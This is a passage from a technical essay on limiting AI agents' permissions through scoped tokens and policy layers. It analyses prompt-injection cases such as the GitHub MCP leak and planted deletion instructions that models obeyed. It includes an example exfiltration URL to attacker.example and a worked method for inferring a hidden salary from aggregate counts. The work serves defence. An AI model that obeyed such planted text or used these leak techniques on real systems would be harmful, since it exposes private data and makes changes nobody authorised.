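| Qwen 2.5 7B | 48.5% | 37.0% | 0% |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 66.0% | 4.0% | 0% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 68.5% | 11.5% | 0% |

In the middle column, the prompt listed every permitted tool by name and forbade all others, yet every model sometimes chose a forbidden one. Claude Haiku 4.5 did so most often in tasks with claims of authority, at 22%.

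The other columns are less informative than they look. In the first, nobody had told the model that any tool was off limits, so the rates measure how much the tasks tempted it to use those tools. The paper's abstract attributes these rates to models that had been "explicitly instructed not to", but the paper's own results contradict this. The zeros in the last column follow from the design, since a model that must choose from a list can't choose a tool that isn't on it. Uppala's proxy, the program that does the filtering between agent and server, also checks each call when it arrives, in case the model produces a tool name from elsewhere.

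Forcing the models to choose a tool probably inflated the middle column as well. In a second experiment, Uppala let them decline and gave them 100 requests that their permitted tools could not satisfy. With rules in the prompt, Haiku made no tool call in 99% of cases, compared with 35% for Qwen and 13% for Llama. The requests were different, so the two experiments aren't strictly comparable, but the results suggest that a model free to do nothing may be safer than the table implies. All three models are small, and larger ones may follow such rules better, though I expect they would still break them sometimes.

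Iyer and Babu (2026), in *Capability Minimization as a Safety Primitive*, go further and change the list at every step of a task. Each tool comes with a description of what must be known before it can run, what it produces and how risky it is. Risky tools also require an authorisation fact, such as "recipient confirmed". The filter looks for the cheapest sequence of tools that reaches the goal, with a score of

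```
score = number of steps + λ × (sum of the steps' risks)
```

where a low-risk tool counts 0, a medium-risk tool 1 and a high-risk tool 4. The number λ sets how many extra steps are worth taking to avoid a risk. A one-step route through a high-risk tool scores 1 + 4λ and a four-step route through low-risk tools scores 4, so the filter prefers the longer route once λ exceeds 0.75. It then shows the agent only the tools for the next step, and withholds a risky one until its authorisation fact is present. An agent asked to summarise an email never sees the tool for sending one.

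The main test used 80 tasks with three versions of a planted instruction each, or 240 trials per method. The agent was a simple program that obeyed every planted instruction whenever the necessary tool was visible. With all 100 tools visible, every attack succeeded. Showing only tools that could run at that moment reduced the success rate to 75%, showing only those on the shortest route to the goal reduced it to 25%, and adding the risk rules reduced it to zero. Iyer and Babu repeated the last two conditions with seven commercially hosted models, including Claude Opus 4 and Amazon's Nova Pro, and got 25% and zero with each.

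The seven identical results mostly reflect the set-up. The 25% is the share of tasks (20 of 80) that Iyer and Babu wrote with a risky shortcut. The models had little opportunity to differ because they had few tools to choose from and, where the hosting service supported it, had to pick one. The results showing when the method fails are more useful. When planted text could forge the authorisation fact, attacks again succeeded in 25% of trials. With λ at 0.5, the filter blocked half the tasks that legitimately needed a risky tool. The guarantee also assumes that the agent can't call a hidden tool by name, a restriction that a server has to enforce.

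The filter has a more basic limitation in preventing leaks, because it decides by tool and not by argument. Iyer and Babu class read-only tools as low risk, with no authorisation needed. The summary task requires `get_issue`, so their filter would show that tool to the agent, which could then call it with `payroll` as the project. Uppala's filter also decides by tool, so it has the same gap, which the token closes.

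### Inferring a hidden value from counts

Suppose the tracker has a reporting tool that returns counts and totals for all 40 projects to anyone with a valid token. The payroll project contains 60 pay correction requests, each with an amount. To protect individuals, the tool does not report on any group of fewer than five issues. The design team filed 12 of the requests, and only one of those came from the Leeds office.

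If the agent asks for the total for designers in Leeds, the tool refuses. It answers the following two queries, because both groups are large enough:

| Group | Issues | Total |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Design team | 12 | €31,000 |
| Design team, outside Leeds | 11 | €22,500 |

Subtracting one row from the other shows one request from a designer in Leeds, for €8,500. The agent has learned that the record exists and what amount it contains without opening any issue in the payroll project.

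Raising the minimum group size doesn't solve the problem. Suppose the tool now refuses groups of fewer than 25. The agent picks any convenient way of splitting the 60 requests, such as the 28 filed before July and the 32 filed later. The Leeds designer's request is one of the later ones. The agent asks about "filed before July, or from a designer in Leeds" and gets 29 issues. It asks about "filed since July, or from a designer in Leeds" and gets 32. Between them, these queries count every request once and the Leeds request one extra time, so

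```
29 + 32 − 60 = 1
```

The same calculation with the totals gives the amount: €78,500 + €80,000 − €150,000 = €8,500. Researchers who study statistical databases call a group used this way a tracker (unrelated to issue trackers).

The tool's developers could record past queries and refuse any that would complete a subtraction, but they would need to recognise every combination that allows one, and an attacker could split the queries between two agents. They could also add random noise to the answers, but this makes the reports less useful to everyone. The cleanest remedy is to compute statistics only over records that the caller's token covers. The agent with the mobile-app token would then get zero for every question about pay corrections, and could learn nothing from counts that it couldn't have read directly.

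A search function can leak values in a similar way if it filters on a field that it doesn't display. An agent can ask whether an amount is above €50,000, then whether it is above the middle of the remaining range, and so on. With ten such questions, it can narrow a figure between zero and €100,000 to a range of about €100. Removing the field from the results is therefore not enough if the agent can still filter on it.

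### The GitHub MCP demonstration

Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) showed how these pieces combine in an attack. The security company set up a GitHub account with several private repositories and a public one for a Pacman game. Anyone can file an issue in a public repository, and the researchers filed one containing instructions for an agent. Then, acting as the account's owner, they asked Claude 4 Opus, connected through GitHub's MCP server, to look at the open issues.

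The agent read the planted issue, fetched information from the private repositories and put it in a pull request (a proposed change to the code) on the public one. Anyone could then read the names of private repositories and the owner's salary and plan to move to South America. Invariant Labs used Claude Desktop, which asks the user to confirm each tool call by default, but observes that many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching.

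*Attack via GitHub MCP server* (heise online) explains that the agent had access to the private data because the server worked on the user's account. The server had no bug in the usual sense. Willison (2025), in *GitHub MCP Exploited*, attributes the leak to a combination of access to private data, exposure to malicious instructions and a way to send information out. The planted text, which he quotes, referred to all of the author's repositories. The attacker didn't need to know their names because the agent could find them itself.

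A token limited to the Pacman repository would have removed the private data from that combination. The agent would still have read the planted issue and might have tried to follow its instructions, but GitHub would have refused its requests for private repositories. If the token had also been read-only, the agent couldn't have opened the pull request with that token. The employee's request concerned one public repository, so neither restriction would have blocked it.

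A one-repository token doesn't help if the secret and the attacker's text are in the same repository. The tracker has the same problem on a smaller scale if the mobile-app issues include customers' email addresses. An attacker can plant a bug report telling the agent to collect the addresses, and the token lets the agent read all of them. Narrower access also doesn't help when a task needs both a public and a private repository, because a token for both gives the agent access to the attacker's text and the secret again.

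Invariant Labs recommends limiting agents to the repositories they need, but considers token permissions too rigid and prefers a rule that lets an agent use only one repository per session. The rule compares the repository named in each call with the one in earlier calls. It has the advantage of adapting to the task without anyone issuing a new token. Invariant Labs sells the software that enforces it. Calls that name no repository, such as a search across the whole account, would need a separate rule.

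GitHub has since addressed the malicious text with a "lockdown mode" for its MCP server (GitHub, 2025). The tool for reading an issue returns an error if the issue's author doesn't have permission to change the repository's code, and the tools for reading comments leave out comments by people without that permission. The mode doesn't affect private repositories. It would probably have stopped the agent in the demonstration from opening the planted issue with the issue-reading tool. It would also stop agents from reading bug reports by members of the public, who are the most likely to file them.

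### Mistaking a partial view for the whole

The employee asks the tracker agent whether anyone has reported that the app crashes at login. The agent searches the 300 issues its token covers, finds nothing and answers no. The employee assumes this answer covers all 12,000 issues, but the server team reported the crash last week in a project that the token doesn't cover.

Services that hide existence well make this error more likely. When a GitHub app has access to only some of an organisation's repositories, a request for all of them returns only those, and GitHub's troubleshooting page suggests checking the credential's access if results seem to be missing. A long-time employee may notice the gap, but an agent that has never seen the full list has nothing to compare it with. An agent that takes a 404 to mean "deleted" may also propose recreating a record that exists but that it can't access.

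Page limits can also leave an agent with incomplete results, whatever its permissions. Most of GitHub's lists return 30 items unless the client asks for more. If the tracker did the same, an agent that stopped after the first page would summarise only 30 of the 300 issues it was supposed to read.

Shortened tool lists have a comparable effect. Uppala tested requests that the permitted tools could not satisfy. Llama made no call in 13% of these cases without filtering and 29% with it. In the other 71%, it called a permitted tool that could not do the job. Qwen improved much more, from 35% to 86%, but its success rate on ordinary permitted tasks fell from 60.7% with rules in the prompt to 48.6% with the filtered list.

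The simplest remedy is to tell the agent what its token covers. The host can put "you can search only the mobile-app project" into the context, and the server can attach the same statement to each list it returns. This reveals only that the tracker may contain other projects. The agent can then report that it found no login crash among the mobile-app issues, and the employee knows to ask the server team.

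## Why reading and changing call for different controls

One token for the mobile-app project could let the tracker agent both read issues and post comments. The argument for leaving out the permission to comment, and sending comments to a policy layer instead, runs as follows:

1. Nobody can recall data once it is in the model's context, so limits on reading have to apply beforehand.
2. Whoever sets up a task can often state which records it needs.
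3. Whether a change is acceptable often depends on its arguments, the state of the system and earlier changes, which nobody knows when the server issues the token.
4. A change can wait for review before it takes effect.
5. So a limit fixed in advance suits reads, and a decision on each call suits changes.

Because two of the premises hold only "often", the conclusion is a default with exceptions.

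### Data already in the context

Once text enters an agent's context, the host sends it to the model with every later request until the host removes it. A salary figure the agent has read can turn up hours later in its final answer, in a message to another agent or in notes it saves for next week. The company could search all of these for the figure, but a filter for "€8,500" misses "eight and a half thousand".

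*SecureClaw* (Ma and Schmid, 2026) controls reading and acting separately because their risks arise at different times. An action does harm when a backend carries it out, whereas an untrusted agent has the data as soon as it arrives. When the agent reads an invoice, a gateway stores the document and gives the agent only a reference number and a short summary with details such as the vendor, amount and due date. To send the invoice, the agent submits a request, which a separate program checks and carries out.

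Ma and Schmid compared SecureClaw with other defences on AgentLeak, which tests whether agents leak private data in final answers, messages between agents or shared memory. Undefended agents leaked data in 93.95% of 496 attacked scenarios, and agents with SecureClaw did so in 3.23%. Faramesh, which checks actions before they run, left the leak rate at 93.95%. It stopped all 2,000 attacks in a different test of unauthorised actions, though its agents completed only 3.7% of their tasks there. Ma and Schmid wrote the policies for Faramesh and used one small model, so another team might get different figures. Still, a control that acts only after the agent has read the data would probably do little to prevent this kind of leak.

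### What a person can specify in advance

The tracker task needs the issues in one project, and the employee knows which one before the agent starts. Reads also rarely affect each other, so the agent learns the same things whether it opens issue 4112 before or after issue 4113, or opens it twice. A fixed set of permitted records is therefore usually enough, although combining harmless answers can produce a harmful one, as subtracting the payroll totals did.

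A person could also approve each read before the tracker answers it, but a read request contains very little to review. It names issue 4112, and the reviewer would have to open the issue to find out whether it contains anything sensitive. The summary task also takes 303 requests. At ten seconds each, the employee would spend about 50 minutes approving them, which is probably longer than skimming the issues would take.

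### A refund of 20 or 10,000 dollars

Suppose an online shop gives a customer service agent a token with the scope `refunds:write`. The agent could make either of these calls:

```
{"name": "issue_refund", "arguments": {"order": 5521, "amount": 20}}
{"name": "issue_refund", "arguments": {"order": 5521, "amount": 10000}}
```

The scope covers both calls. If the shop uses the structured format described earlier, it can write a maximum of $50 per refund into the token, and the payment service will refuse the second call. The agent can still pay out $10,000 in 200 refunds of $50.

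Even the $20 refund may be wrong. The order may have cost $12, the customer may not have returned anything, or a colleague may have refunded it already. If the authorization server issues the token at 9:00 and the colleague pays the refund at 9:40, no wording of the scope could have accounted for that. *Compromise Is Not Consequence* (Hagverdiyev, 2026) reports a duplicate of a legitimate payment in a pilot run with a scoped token. The token limited which payments the agent could make, but not how many times it could make them.

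Changes that are acceptable individually can also cause problems in combination. *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail* (Trofimov and Novikov, 2026) describes an agent with €1,500 to spend on a trip. To save time, it books a €900 flight and a €700 hotel in parallel. Both bookings succeed, which puts the trip €100 over budget. The agent cancels the hotel, but the flight is non-refundable, so the user has paid for a flight and has no hotel.

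Several recent systems therefore wait for facts that appear only during the task. *PolicyGuide* (2026) blocks each tool that makes changes until other tools have confirmed the facts that the policy requires. *ToolFence* (2026) can withhold a call until the agent has read the missing evidence. *Agenra* (2026) supports quotas and counts each permitted attempt against the quota, even if nobody knows whether the call succeeded.

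All of this requires the change to wait, and most changes can. A proposed refund contains the order and the amount, so a reviewer can look up the order and decide before any money moves. In SecureClaw, each approval applies to one exact request. If the agent gets approval to send an invoice to one address and then substitutes another, the program that sends it recomputes a code over the whole request and blocks the invoice because the code doesn't match the approval.

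Some changes are useless if delayed. Trofimov and Novikov give the example of an agent negotiating for a user, which can't learn the other side's reaction without making an offer. The flight is an easier case because the agent could ask for a quote or place a hold that expires, and commit only once it knew both prices.

### The scoped-deletion trials

*Instruction Self-Arbitration Is Not a Trust Boundary* (Leong, 2026) tested what happens when the token itself permits changes. The trials used GPT-5.1, Claude Sonnet 5 and Gemini 2.5 Pro in a sandbox with a real directory tree. The software around the model held a token, hidden from the model, that allowed deletions in one directory, `/workspace/temp`. The model then received a validly signed record whose text asked for a deletion. Such a record can occur outside a laboratory when a legitimate program stores and signs something that an attacker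 wrote.

If the model called the deletion tool, a checker compared the path in the call with the token's scope. Leong compared file lists from before and after each trial to see what the agent had deleted.

| Target named in the record | Trials | Attempted deletions | Trials with a deletion |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Outside the directory | 36 | 31 | 0 |
| Outside, through a path containing `../` | 36 | 21 | 0 |
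| Outside, through a symbolic link | 36 | 34 | 0 |
| Inside the directory | 42 | 41 | 31 |

The zeros largely follow from the design, since the checker refuses any path outside the scope. Leong says the trials test whether the checks work on calls that models really produce, and don't estimate how well they would withstand an attacker who adapts. Symbolic links, which are entries that point to another location, were the hardest case. A simpler checker that compared only the text of the paths would have allowed all 34 of those attempts. The trials did not test limits on reading, because the tool for listing files accepted any path the model gave it.

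Inside the directory, GPT-5.1 and Gemini each deleted something in all 14 of their trials, and Claude did in 3 of 14. A limit on output length had cut off many of Claude's replies. When Leong raised the limit, Claude's count rose to 8, and the total for the three models rose from 31 to 36 of 42.

The checker made no mistake in those 31 trials. In 120 of 150 other trials, the agents used the same scope to carry out deletions that the owner had approved. An approved deletion and an induced one can use the same tool, path and token. They differ in who wanted the deletion, which the token doesn't record. Narrowing the scope to a single file would reduce the damage, but an attacker could still get the agent to delete that file.

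*AIRGuard* (2026) proposes that in such cases anything the agent reads may inform it, but only the user's task, a trusted policy or explicit consent can authorise a side effect. To apply this rule, a program or person has to compare each proposed change with what the user asked for. This comparison can fail too. In Ma and Schmid's tests on AgentDojo, another set of simulated attacks, 4 of 629 attacks still succeeded with both of their controls in place. The policy permitted all four actions, and in three of them the rules didn't tie the action closely enough to the right person or context.

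### Reads that act and changes that reveal

*The Read-Only Tool*, a description of a design pattern for agents, opens with the claim that "a tool that only reads is a tool that cannot break anything". It then requires such a tool to have no side effects, including logging that changes state. Few real tools meet that standard. Opening an email usually marks it as read, and a large query can slow down a live database. Most of these effects are harmless, but reading a message from a work queue can also remove it, so that no other program will process it. The company should treat such a read as a change.

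Reads can also carry data out. If the tracker agent can fetch web pages, an attacker might plant an instruction to open `https://attacker.example/log?salary=8500`. The agent only requests a page, but the request sends the salary to the attacker's server. A read-only token for the tracker doesn't help, because the request never goes to the tracker. Whether the request is acceptable depends on its address argument, so the company needs to check each address or let the agent reach only a fixed list of sites.

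Conversely, a change can let an agent read data its token doesn't cover, because many services reply to a change with the full updated record. Suppose the agent proposes a comment on payroll issue 87, and the policy layer posts it and passes back the tracker's reply. The agent now has the issue's title and description, although its token doesn't cover the payroll project. The policy layer can avoid this by returning only "posted" or "refused". A change can also publish what the agent read elsewhere, as the pull request did in the GitHub MCP leak, so some policy layers have rules that link reads to later writes.

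### Reads that need judgement and changes that don't

For some tasks, nobody can list the records an agent will need before the task starts. A token issued in the morning to a shop's customer service agent can't be limited to the customers who will call that day, and a token for all customers would let one misled agent read everybody's records. The shop could issue a token for one customer when that customer calls and proves who they are. If it has no system that can do this, a gateway has to check each read using whatever information it has about the call. The gateway must still allow or block the read before the record reaches the agent.

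A company can rule out many changes before a task starts. For example, an agent that summarises files never needs to delete one. Hagverdiyev tested such limits on 128 invented tasks involving files, calendars, mail and payments. In each task, the model read planted text that urged it to do something else, such as delete the file it was supposed to summarise. Hagverdiyev recorded the model's next request and submitted it under a broad token and under three arrangements with scoped tokens.

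The five small models tested made 2,054 requests that went beyond their tasks. Under the broad token, 1,649 of them ran, and the rest failed for other reasons. None ran under any of the three scoped arrangements, which also blocked no request that the task permitted. The requests were identical, so the difference can't be due to a model behaving better in some runs. As Hagverdiyev points out, a correctly enforced scope should stop every such request, and the researcher had written every scope by hand. The experiment therefore shows what a good scope prevents, but not how easily people can write one for real work.

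A fixed limit is also easier to get right than a rule that checks the arguments of each call. If the tracker agent has no way to delete issues, nobody has to decide which deletions to allow.

### Deciding which calls are reads

To control reads and changes differently, a system has to tell which calls are which. Sorting them by tool works for `get_issue` and `add_comment`, but not for a tool such as `run_sql`, which can list a table or erase it depending on the query. *Agentao* (2026), a framework for running agents, has a read-only mode that allows only tools marked as read-only. This is a sensible default, but a tool marked read-only by mistake can still make changes.

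MCP has a standard set of tool annotations. `readOnlyHint` means that a tool doesn't modify anything, and `destructiveHint` means that its changes may destroy something rather than only add to it. Two others cover whether repeating a call is safe and whether the tool interacts with the outside world. Clients should assume that a tool without annotations can change things and may be destructive.

The server's developers write these labels, and the protocol doesn't check them against the code. A server can label a tool read-only and still use it to delete the user's files, as Model Context Protocol (2026) acknowledges. When developers first proposed the labels, one of MCP's creators asked how a client could use information it couldn't trust. As a compromise, the protocol calls every label a hint and requires clients to distrust hints from untrusted servers. Model Context Protocol's reference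 page *Class ToolAnnotations* says clients should never base decisions about using a tool on hints from untrusted servers. A company that runs its own servers can rely on the labels more because it can inspect the code behind them.

Honest developers often leave the labels out. Trofimov and Novikov collected the definitions of 98,291 tools from public MCP servers and found no labels on 26% of them. That share rises to 47.2% without one publisher, which supplied 45% of the tools and labels everything. Some tools also have written descriptions that don't match their code, according to *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers* (2026), which recommends that developers disclose any behaviour that changes data.

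Even a correct label may have no effect. Yao, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *When Neither Side Confirms*, traced what 41 open-source hosts and developer kits do by default when a model calls a tool. In 39 of them, labelling a tool as destructive changed nothing, and 32 had no approval step for ordinary calls. The researchers also built a small server with a note-deletion tool correctly labelled as destructive, and connected it to five inexpensive models through four developer kits. The list of notes contained a planted instruction to delete the user's tax records. The models tried to delete them in 180 of 400 runs, and all 180 deletions went through.

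In another version, the tool refused to delete anything unless the call contained `confirm=true`. When the planted text didn't mention this setting, the models tried the deletion in 169 runs and supplied the confirmation themselves in 127. A confirmation setting therefore doesn't ensure that anyone reviews the call if the model can fill it in itself.

The labels would do more good if hosts asked for approval whenever a tool wasn't labeled safe. Yao and colleagues paired destructive tools with 25 applications and estimated that this default would cut the share of pairs with no enforced human approval from 60.7% to 5.4%. The remaining 5.4% involve destructive tools wrongly labeled safe. The default would also produce many more prompts for harmless tools. Read-only labels are less trustworthy than destructive ones because a malicious server has a strong reason to label a destructive tool read-only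 but little reason to label a harmless tool destructive.

A read-only token avoids some of this because the backend distinguishes reads from changes. The tracker will reject a change even if the tool is wrongly labeled "read-only", as long as the server doesn't use a broader key of its own to access the tracker.

### Both controls on one call

For most reads, the main question is whether the agent may have the data at all. For most changes, it is whether this particular change should happen now. The separation between token and policy layer follows these questions, and many calls raise both:

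| Call | What a fixed limit can settle | What remains to decide on the call |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Open issue 4112 | The project and the operation | Usually nothing |
| Look up a caller's order history | The service and the kind of record | Whether this customer is calling |
| Fetch a web page | The permitted sites | What the address gives away |
| Comment on issue 4112 | The project | The text, and any private data in it |
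| Refund order 5521 | The shop, and perhaps a maximum | The amount, the order's state and earlier refunds |

A policy layer that approves refunds still benefits from a narrow token. The shop can limit the token used by the program that pays refunds to at most $50 per refund. If someone makes a mistake in the policy layer's rule about amounts, the payment service will still refuse a single $10,000 refund.

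## How a policy layer decides on a proposed change

The tracker agent's token can't post comments, so the host sends each proposed comment to the policy layer, which has its own credential for posting. The policy layer has to determine who is asking and what the call would do. It then applies the company's rules and permits the comment, denies it, or holds it for a person to review.

### From a tool call to a question for the rules

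Suppose the agent proposes this call:

```
{"name": "add_comment",
 "arguments": {"project": "mobile-app", "issue": 4112,
               "text": "No activity since March. Can we close this?"}}
```

The model writes the whole tool call, so nothing in the call can prove who sent it. If the tool had an argument called `acting_as`, a planted instruction could get the model to fill in "administrator". The sender's identity has to come from a credential that the model can't write. Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, describe a policy layer called FORGE that works this way. The software around the agent attaches a certificate, a login token or an API key to each request, and the policy engine verifies it before applying any rule. They put this check in the engine so that the agent's software can't simply claim to be someone else.

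The policy layer then translates the call into an action, a resource and details. The resource is the easiest part to get wrong. If the tracker finds issues by number alone and issue 87 belongs to the payroll project, a call that names mobile-app and issue 87 could satisfy a rule about mobile-app but post in payroll. The policy layer should look up which project the issue belongs to and ignore the project the model named.

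Tools that run whole commands are harder to translate. Microsoft's *Tool Access Policies* describes the rules for Azure SRE Agent, an agent that helps engineers run cloud systems. An administrator can block commands by their text. For example, the pattern `bash(az * delete *)` blocks deletions through Azure's command line. The pattern covers the shell tools but not the Python tool, so a Python script that deletes the same resource needs its own rule.

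### Three rules and four calls

Cedar is an open-source language for access rules, developed by Amazon's cloud division, AWS. AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026) announced a policy layer that uses it. A gateway outside the agent's code intercepts each tool call and evaluates it against the rules. AWS says that once a policy is attached to the gateway, the gateway blocks every call unless a rule permits it.

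In Cedar, the tracker's rules for comments could look like this, with names invented for the example:

```
// Rule 1
permit (
  principal == Agent::"summary-agent",
  action == Action::"add_comment",
  resource in Project::"mobile-app"
);

// Rule 2
forbid (principal, action == Action::"add_comment", resource)
when { context.text_length > 500 };

// Rule 3
forbid (principal, action == Action::"add_comment", resource)
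when { resource.customer_visible }
unless { context.approved };
```

Rule 1 lets the agent comment on issues in the mobile-app project. Rule 2 blocks comments longer than 500 characters, whoever writes them. Rule 3 blocks comments on issues that customers can read, unless a person has approved the comment. The policy layer supplies everything under `context`, including `approved`. If the agent could set `approved`, the model might well fill it in, as the models in Yao and colleagues' tests did with `confirm=true`.

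| Proposed comment | Matching rules | Cedar's answer | What the policy layer does |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| 180 characters on issue 4112, which only staff can read | 1 | Allow | Posts it |
| 180 characters on payroll issue 87, which only staff can read | None | Deny | Refuses it |
| 2,400 characters on issue 4112 | 1 and 2 | Deny | Refuses it |
| 150 characters on mobile-app issue 4120, which customers can read | 1 and 3 | Deny | Holds it for a person |

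Nobody wrote a rule about payroll, so no rule permits the second call and Cedar denies it. The term for this in Cedar's documentation is an implicit deny. This default protects the company against cases its staff never thought of, but it also blocks some harmless ones.

Cedar returns only "allow" or "deny", so the policy layer has to determine when to hold a call for approval. One way is to evaluate a denied call again as if a person had approved it. The result for the comment on issue 4120 changes to "allow", so it is worth asking someone. The 2,400-character comment is still denied, so a prompt would waste the employee's time.

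A rule can also fail to run, for example because the tracker didn't report whether customers can read an issue. Cedar still returns a decision and lists the failed rule with it. If rule 3 fails, rule 1 is enough to permit the comment, so the policy layer should treat any such error as a denial.

AWS also lets teams write their rules in ordinary language, and its software converts them to Cedar. Palumbo and colleagues offer a similar conversion for FORGE and warn that the language model doing it may omit a condition or invent one. They recommend checking that every requirement has a rule and that every rule comes from a requirement.

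### Which rule wins

In Cedar, one matching `forbid` rule overrides all matching `permit` rules, and rule order doesn't matter. AWS used automated reasoning to prove that Cedar's decision procedure has both properties. A security team can therefore write rule 2 knowing that nobody can undo it by adding a `permit` rule elsewhere. Any exception has to go in the `forbid` rule itself, like the `unless` clause in rule 3.

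Azure SRE Agent checks its rules in the order deny, allow, ask. Administrators can write all three kinds for the whole system, while an ordinary user can add only "allow" rules for one conversation. A user's "allow" can't override an administrator's "deny", but it does override an "ask", so any user can remove an administrator's approval requirement for the length of a conversation. Microsoft presents this as a way to skip approval for a tool the user has already validated. If no rule matches, the tool runs unless some other setting requires approval.

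Azure's hooks make precedence harder to reason about. A hook is a script or a language model that evaluates a call in context, and it runs before the rules. If a user-defined hook returns "allow", the call goes ahead even if a system-wide rule denies it. Suppose an administrator denies all deletions and a colleague adds a hook that allows them in the test environment. The agent can now delete things there, even though the rules still ban it.

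This design is defensible. A hook can account for circumstances that a text pattern can't express. Only administrators can create hooks, and an administrator could presumably remove the "deny" rule anyway. The system also logs every override.

If hooks can override a "deny" rule, an auditor has to read every hook as well as the rules to know what the agent can't do. If the hook is a language model, planted text that reaches it might also cause it to allow the call. The ban would then depend on a model's judgement, which the rule alone did not require. It would be safer to let hooks add denials but never remove them, and to write exceptions into the "deny" rule. But during an outage, an administrator would have to edit the rule before the agent could act.

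### Limits on arguments and totals

Rules that check only which tool is called miss calls that use the right tool with the wrong argument. Ji, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems*, demonstrated this on CaMeL, a defence that plans the sequence of tool calls from the user's request before the agent reads any outside text. A homeowner asked the agent to give their daughter access to the front door, using the ID in a recent message. An attacker had added text containing a different ID to that message. The agent made exactly the planned calls and gave the attacker access. A rule that compared the ID with a list of family members would have stopped the attack.

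A limit on totals needs a memory of earlier calls, which Cedar's rules don't have. According to AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies*, each rule depends only on the current request and the context and tags supplied with it. To limit the agent to 20 comments an hour, the policy layer has to keep the count itself and pass it in:

```
forbid (principal, action == Action::"add_comment", resource)
when { context.comments_this_hour >= 20 };
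```

A limit of 20 comments an hour can fail in several ways, depending on how the policy layer counts. Suppose the agent has posted 19 comments and proposes five more at once. If the layer checks all five before it posts any, each check uses a count of 19, so all five pass and the agent ends up with 24. To prevent this, the layer has to increase the count as part of the check. If the count restarts on the hour, the agent can post 20 comments at 9:59 and another 20 at 10:00. And if every agent has its own counter, ten agents working for one employee can post 200. A daily maximum would have the same problems for the shop whose agent could pay out $10,000 in $50 refunds.

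FORGE keeps a record of messages, tool calls and results that its rules can refer to. In one deployment, it stopped a coding agent from publishing changes until security scans had covered every recent edit. But its rule language has no built-in support for time, so an hourly limit requires manual bookkeeping.

### Executing the request that was checked

The check is useless if the tracker receives a different request from the one the policy layer examined. This can happen without any tampering in between. A model might produce arguments that contain the same name twice:

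```
{"issue": 4112, "issue": 87, "text": "..."}
```

When a request gives the same field more than one value, some programs use the first value and others use the last. If the policy layer reads 4112 and the tracker reads 87, the policy layer approves a comment for the mobile-app project, but the tracker posts it in the payroll project.

*The Agent Access Model*, a proposal by Silverlock from the network and security company Cloudflare, describes a remedy that uses a program called an adapter. The adapter builds one complete version of the request, including the operation, resource, recipient and every argument that affects its reach. It then freezes that version, the policy layer checks it, and the adapter executes exactly what was checked. In the example with two issue numbers, the adapter would choose one before the check, and the tracker would never receive the other.

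Freezing matters most for held requests, because hours may pass between proposal and approval. As with SecureClaw's approvals, the agent can't swap in a different comment afterwards, but the tracker can still change. If a colleague makes issue 4112 visible to customers while the comment is awaiting approval, the comment may no longer be acceptable. The policy layer should evaluate its rules again just before it posts. This still leaves a short gap between the check and the post, unless the tracker can reject the comment if the issue has changed since the check.

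### Cloudflare's Agent Access Model

Cloudflare's Agent Access Model, published in August 2026, is a vendor's proposed architecture with no measured trial reported. It combines a narrow credential with a policy layer and adds the principle that an agent's permissions can only shrink during a task.

The permissions start from a ceiling. Someone writes a template for each kind of task, such as "reconciliation may read these tables and post to this channel". When a task starts, the system computes

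```
ceiling = template ∩ rights of the person or system starting the task
                   ∩ rights of the agent service
```

and then applies the policies of the resource owners and the organisation. The agent gets a credential that expires no later than the task does. The credential is tied to a key that the model never receives. The step-up requests described earlier can't raise the ceiling, so work that needs more access has to start as a new task.

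The system checks every action within the ceiling against the agent's identity, its task and what the task has already touched. The harness, the software that carries out the model's tool calls, checks the operation and its arguments. Network controls separately limit which outside addresses the agent's traffic can reach, so they may still block a bad request that a bug in the harness lets through. The harness and the network controls both depend on a shared record of the task's permissions, so Silverlock requires them to block requests when that record is unavailable.

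The most distinctive part is the Trust Ratchet, which removes outward channels once the agent reads protected data. Silverlock illustrates it with a nightly job that compares a payment processor's report with a company's ledgers:

1. The ceiling covers the processor's report, two ledgers, a vendor-support operation and a message to the finance team. It lasts ten minutes.
2. The agent requests the report. The policy classifies it as protected, so the harness keeps it out of the model's context for now.
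3. The system withdraws access to the processor and to vendor support. The harness stops any work that relied on them and the network closes open connections. If any of these components fails to confirm the change, the agent never gets the report.
4. The agent receives the report and reads the ledgers. A memo in one ledger contains a planted instruction to attach the full account history to a support case.
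5. The agent tries to do so, and the harness refuses. The operation was within the original ceiling, but the agent no longer has access to it.

The third step has to come before the fourth, because an agent that already had the report could send it out while the system was still closing the channels.

The finance message remains open, so Silverlock restricts its contents. The adapter stores the result in a fixed format with a status and numeric totals but no free text. The agent receives only an identifier for the stored result and can post nothing else.

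This works for reconciliation because the task needs only numbers. But the tracker agent alternates between reading issues and writing comments. If reading an issue removed its permission to comment, it could post nothing after reading the first issue. If the policy kept the permission, the agent could copy what it had read into a comment, since comments are free text. Silverlock acknowledges that a broad ratchet will block harmless activity, and that even a narrow one can't prevent leaks through an approved destination that an attacker has compromised.

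The proposal includes a log-based review of permissions to improve the templates. The components that enforce the rules produce the logs, so the review doesn't rely on the model's account of its actions. If a permission goes unused over many successful runs, the system proposes removing it. If the same denial repeatedly coincides with failed work, it may propose adding a permission. A person decides whether to approve each change, and approved changes affect only future tasks. Silverlock gives good reasons for this caution: an attacker can repeat a forbidden action until it looks routine, and an unused permission may be there for a rare emergency.

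The model assumes that each task has one source of authority. Suppose an agent serves a channel shared by Alice, who may see revenue figures, and Bob, who may not. If it summarises a thread containing those figures for Alice and reuses the summary for Bob, it has leaked them. Silverlock doesn't claim to solve this. The options are to keep Alice's and Bob's work separate or to limit the agent to what both may see, which makes it less useful.

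### Progent, SEAgent and FORGE

Three research groups have measured their own policy layers, which differ mainly in who writes the rules and what the rules can refer to.

In *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025), a language model writes rules for each task from the user's request. The rules name tools and set conditions on their arguments. As in Cedar, a "forbid" rule overrides any rule that allows the call, and a call that matches no rule is denied. The model then proposes updates to the rules as the agent learns more. These updates may draw on text that an attacker planted, and *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that such text could loosen the rules.

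Progent's current version addresses this with a solver, a program that can decide whether a logical formula holds in every case. If A(P) is the set of calls that the rules P permit, the solver checks whether

```
A(new rules) ⊆ A(old rules)
```

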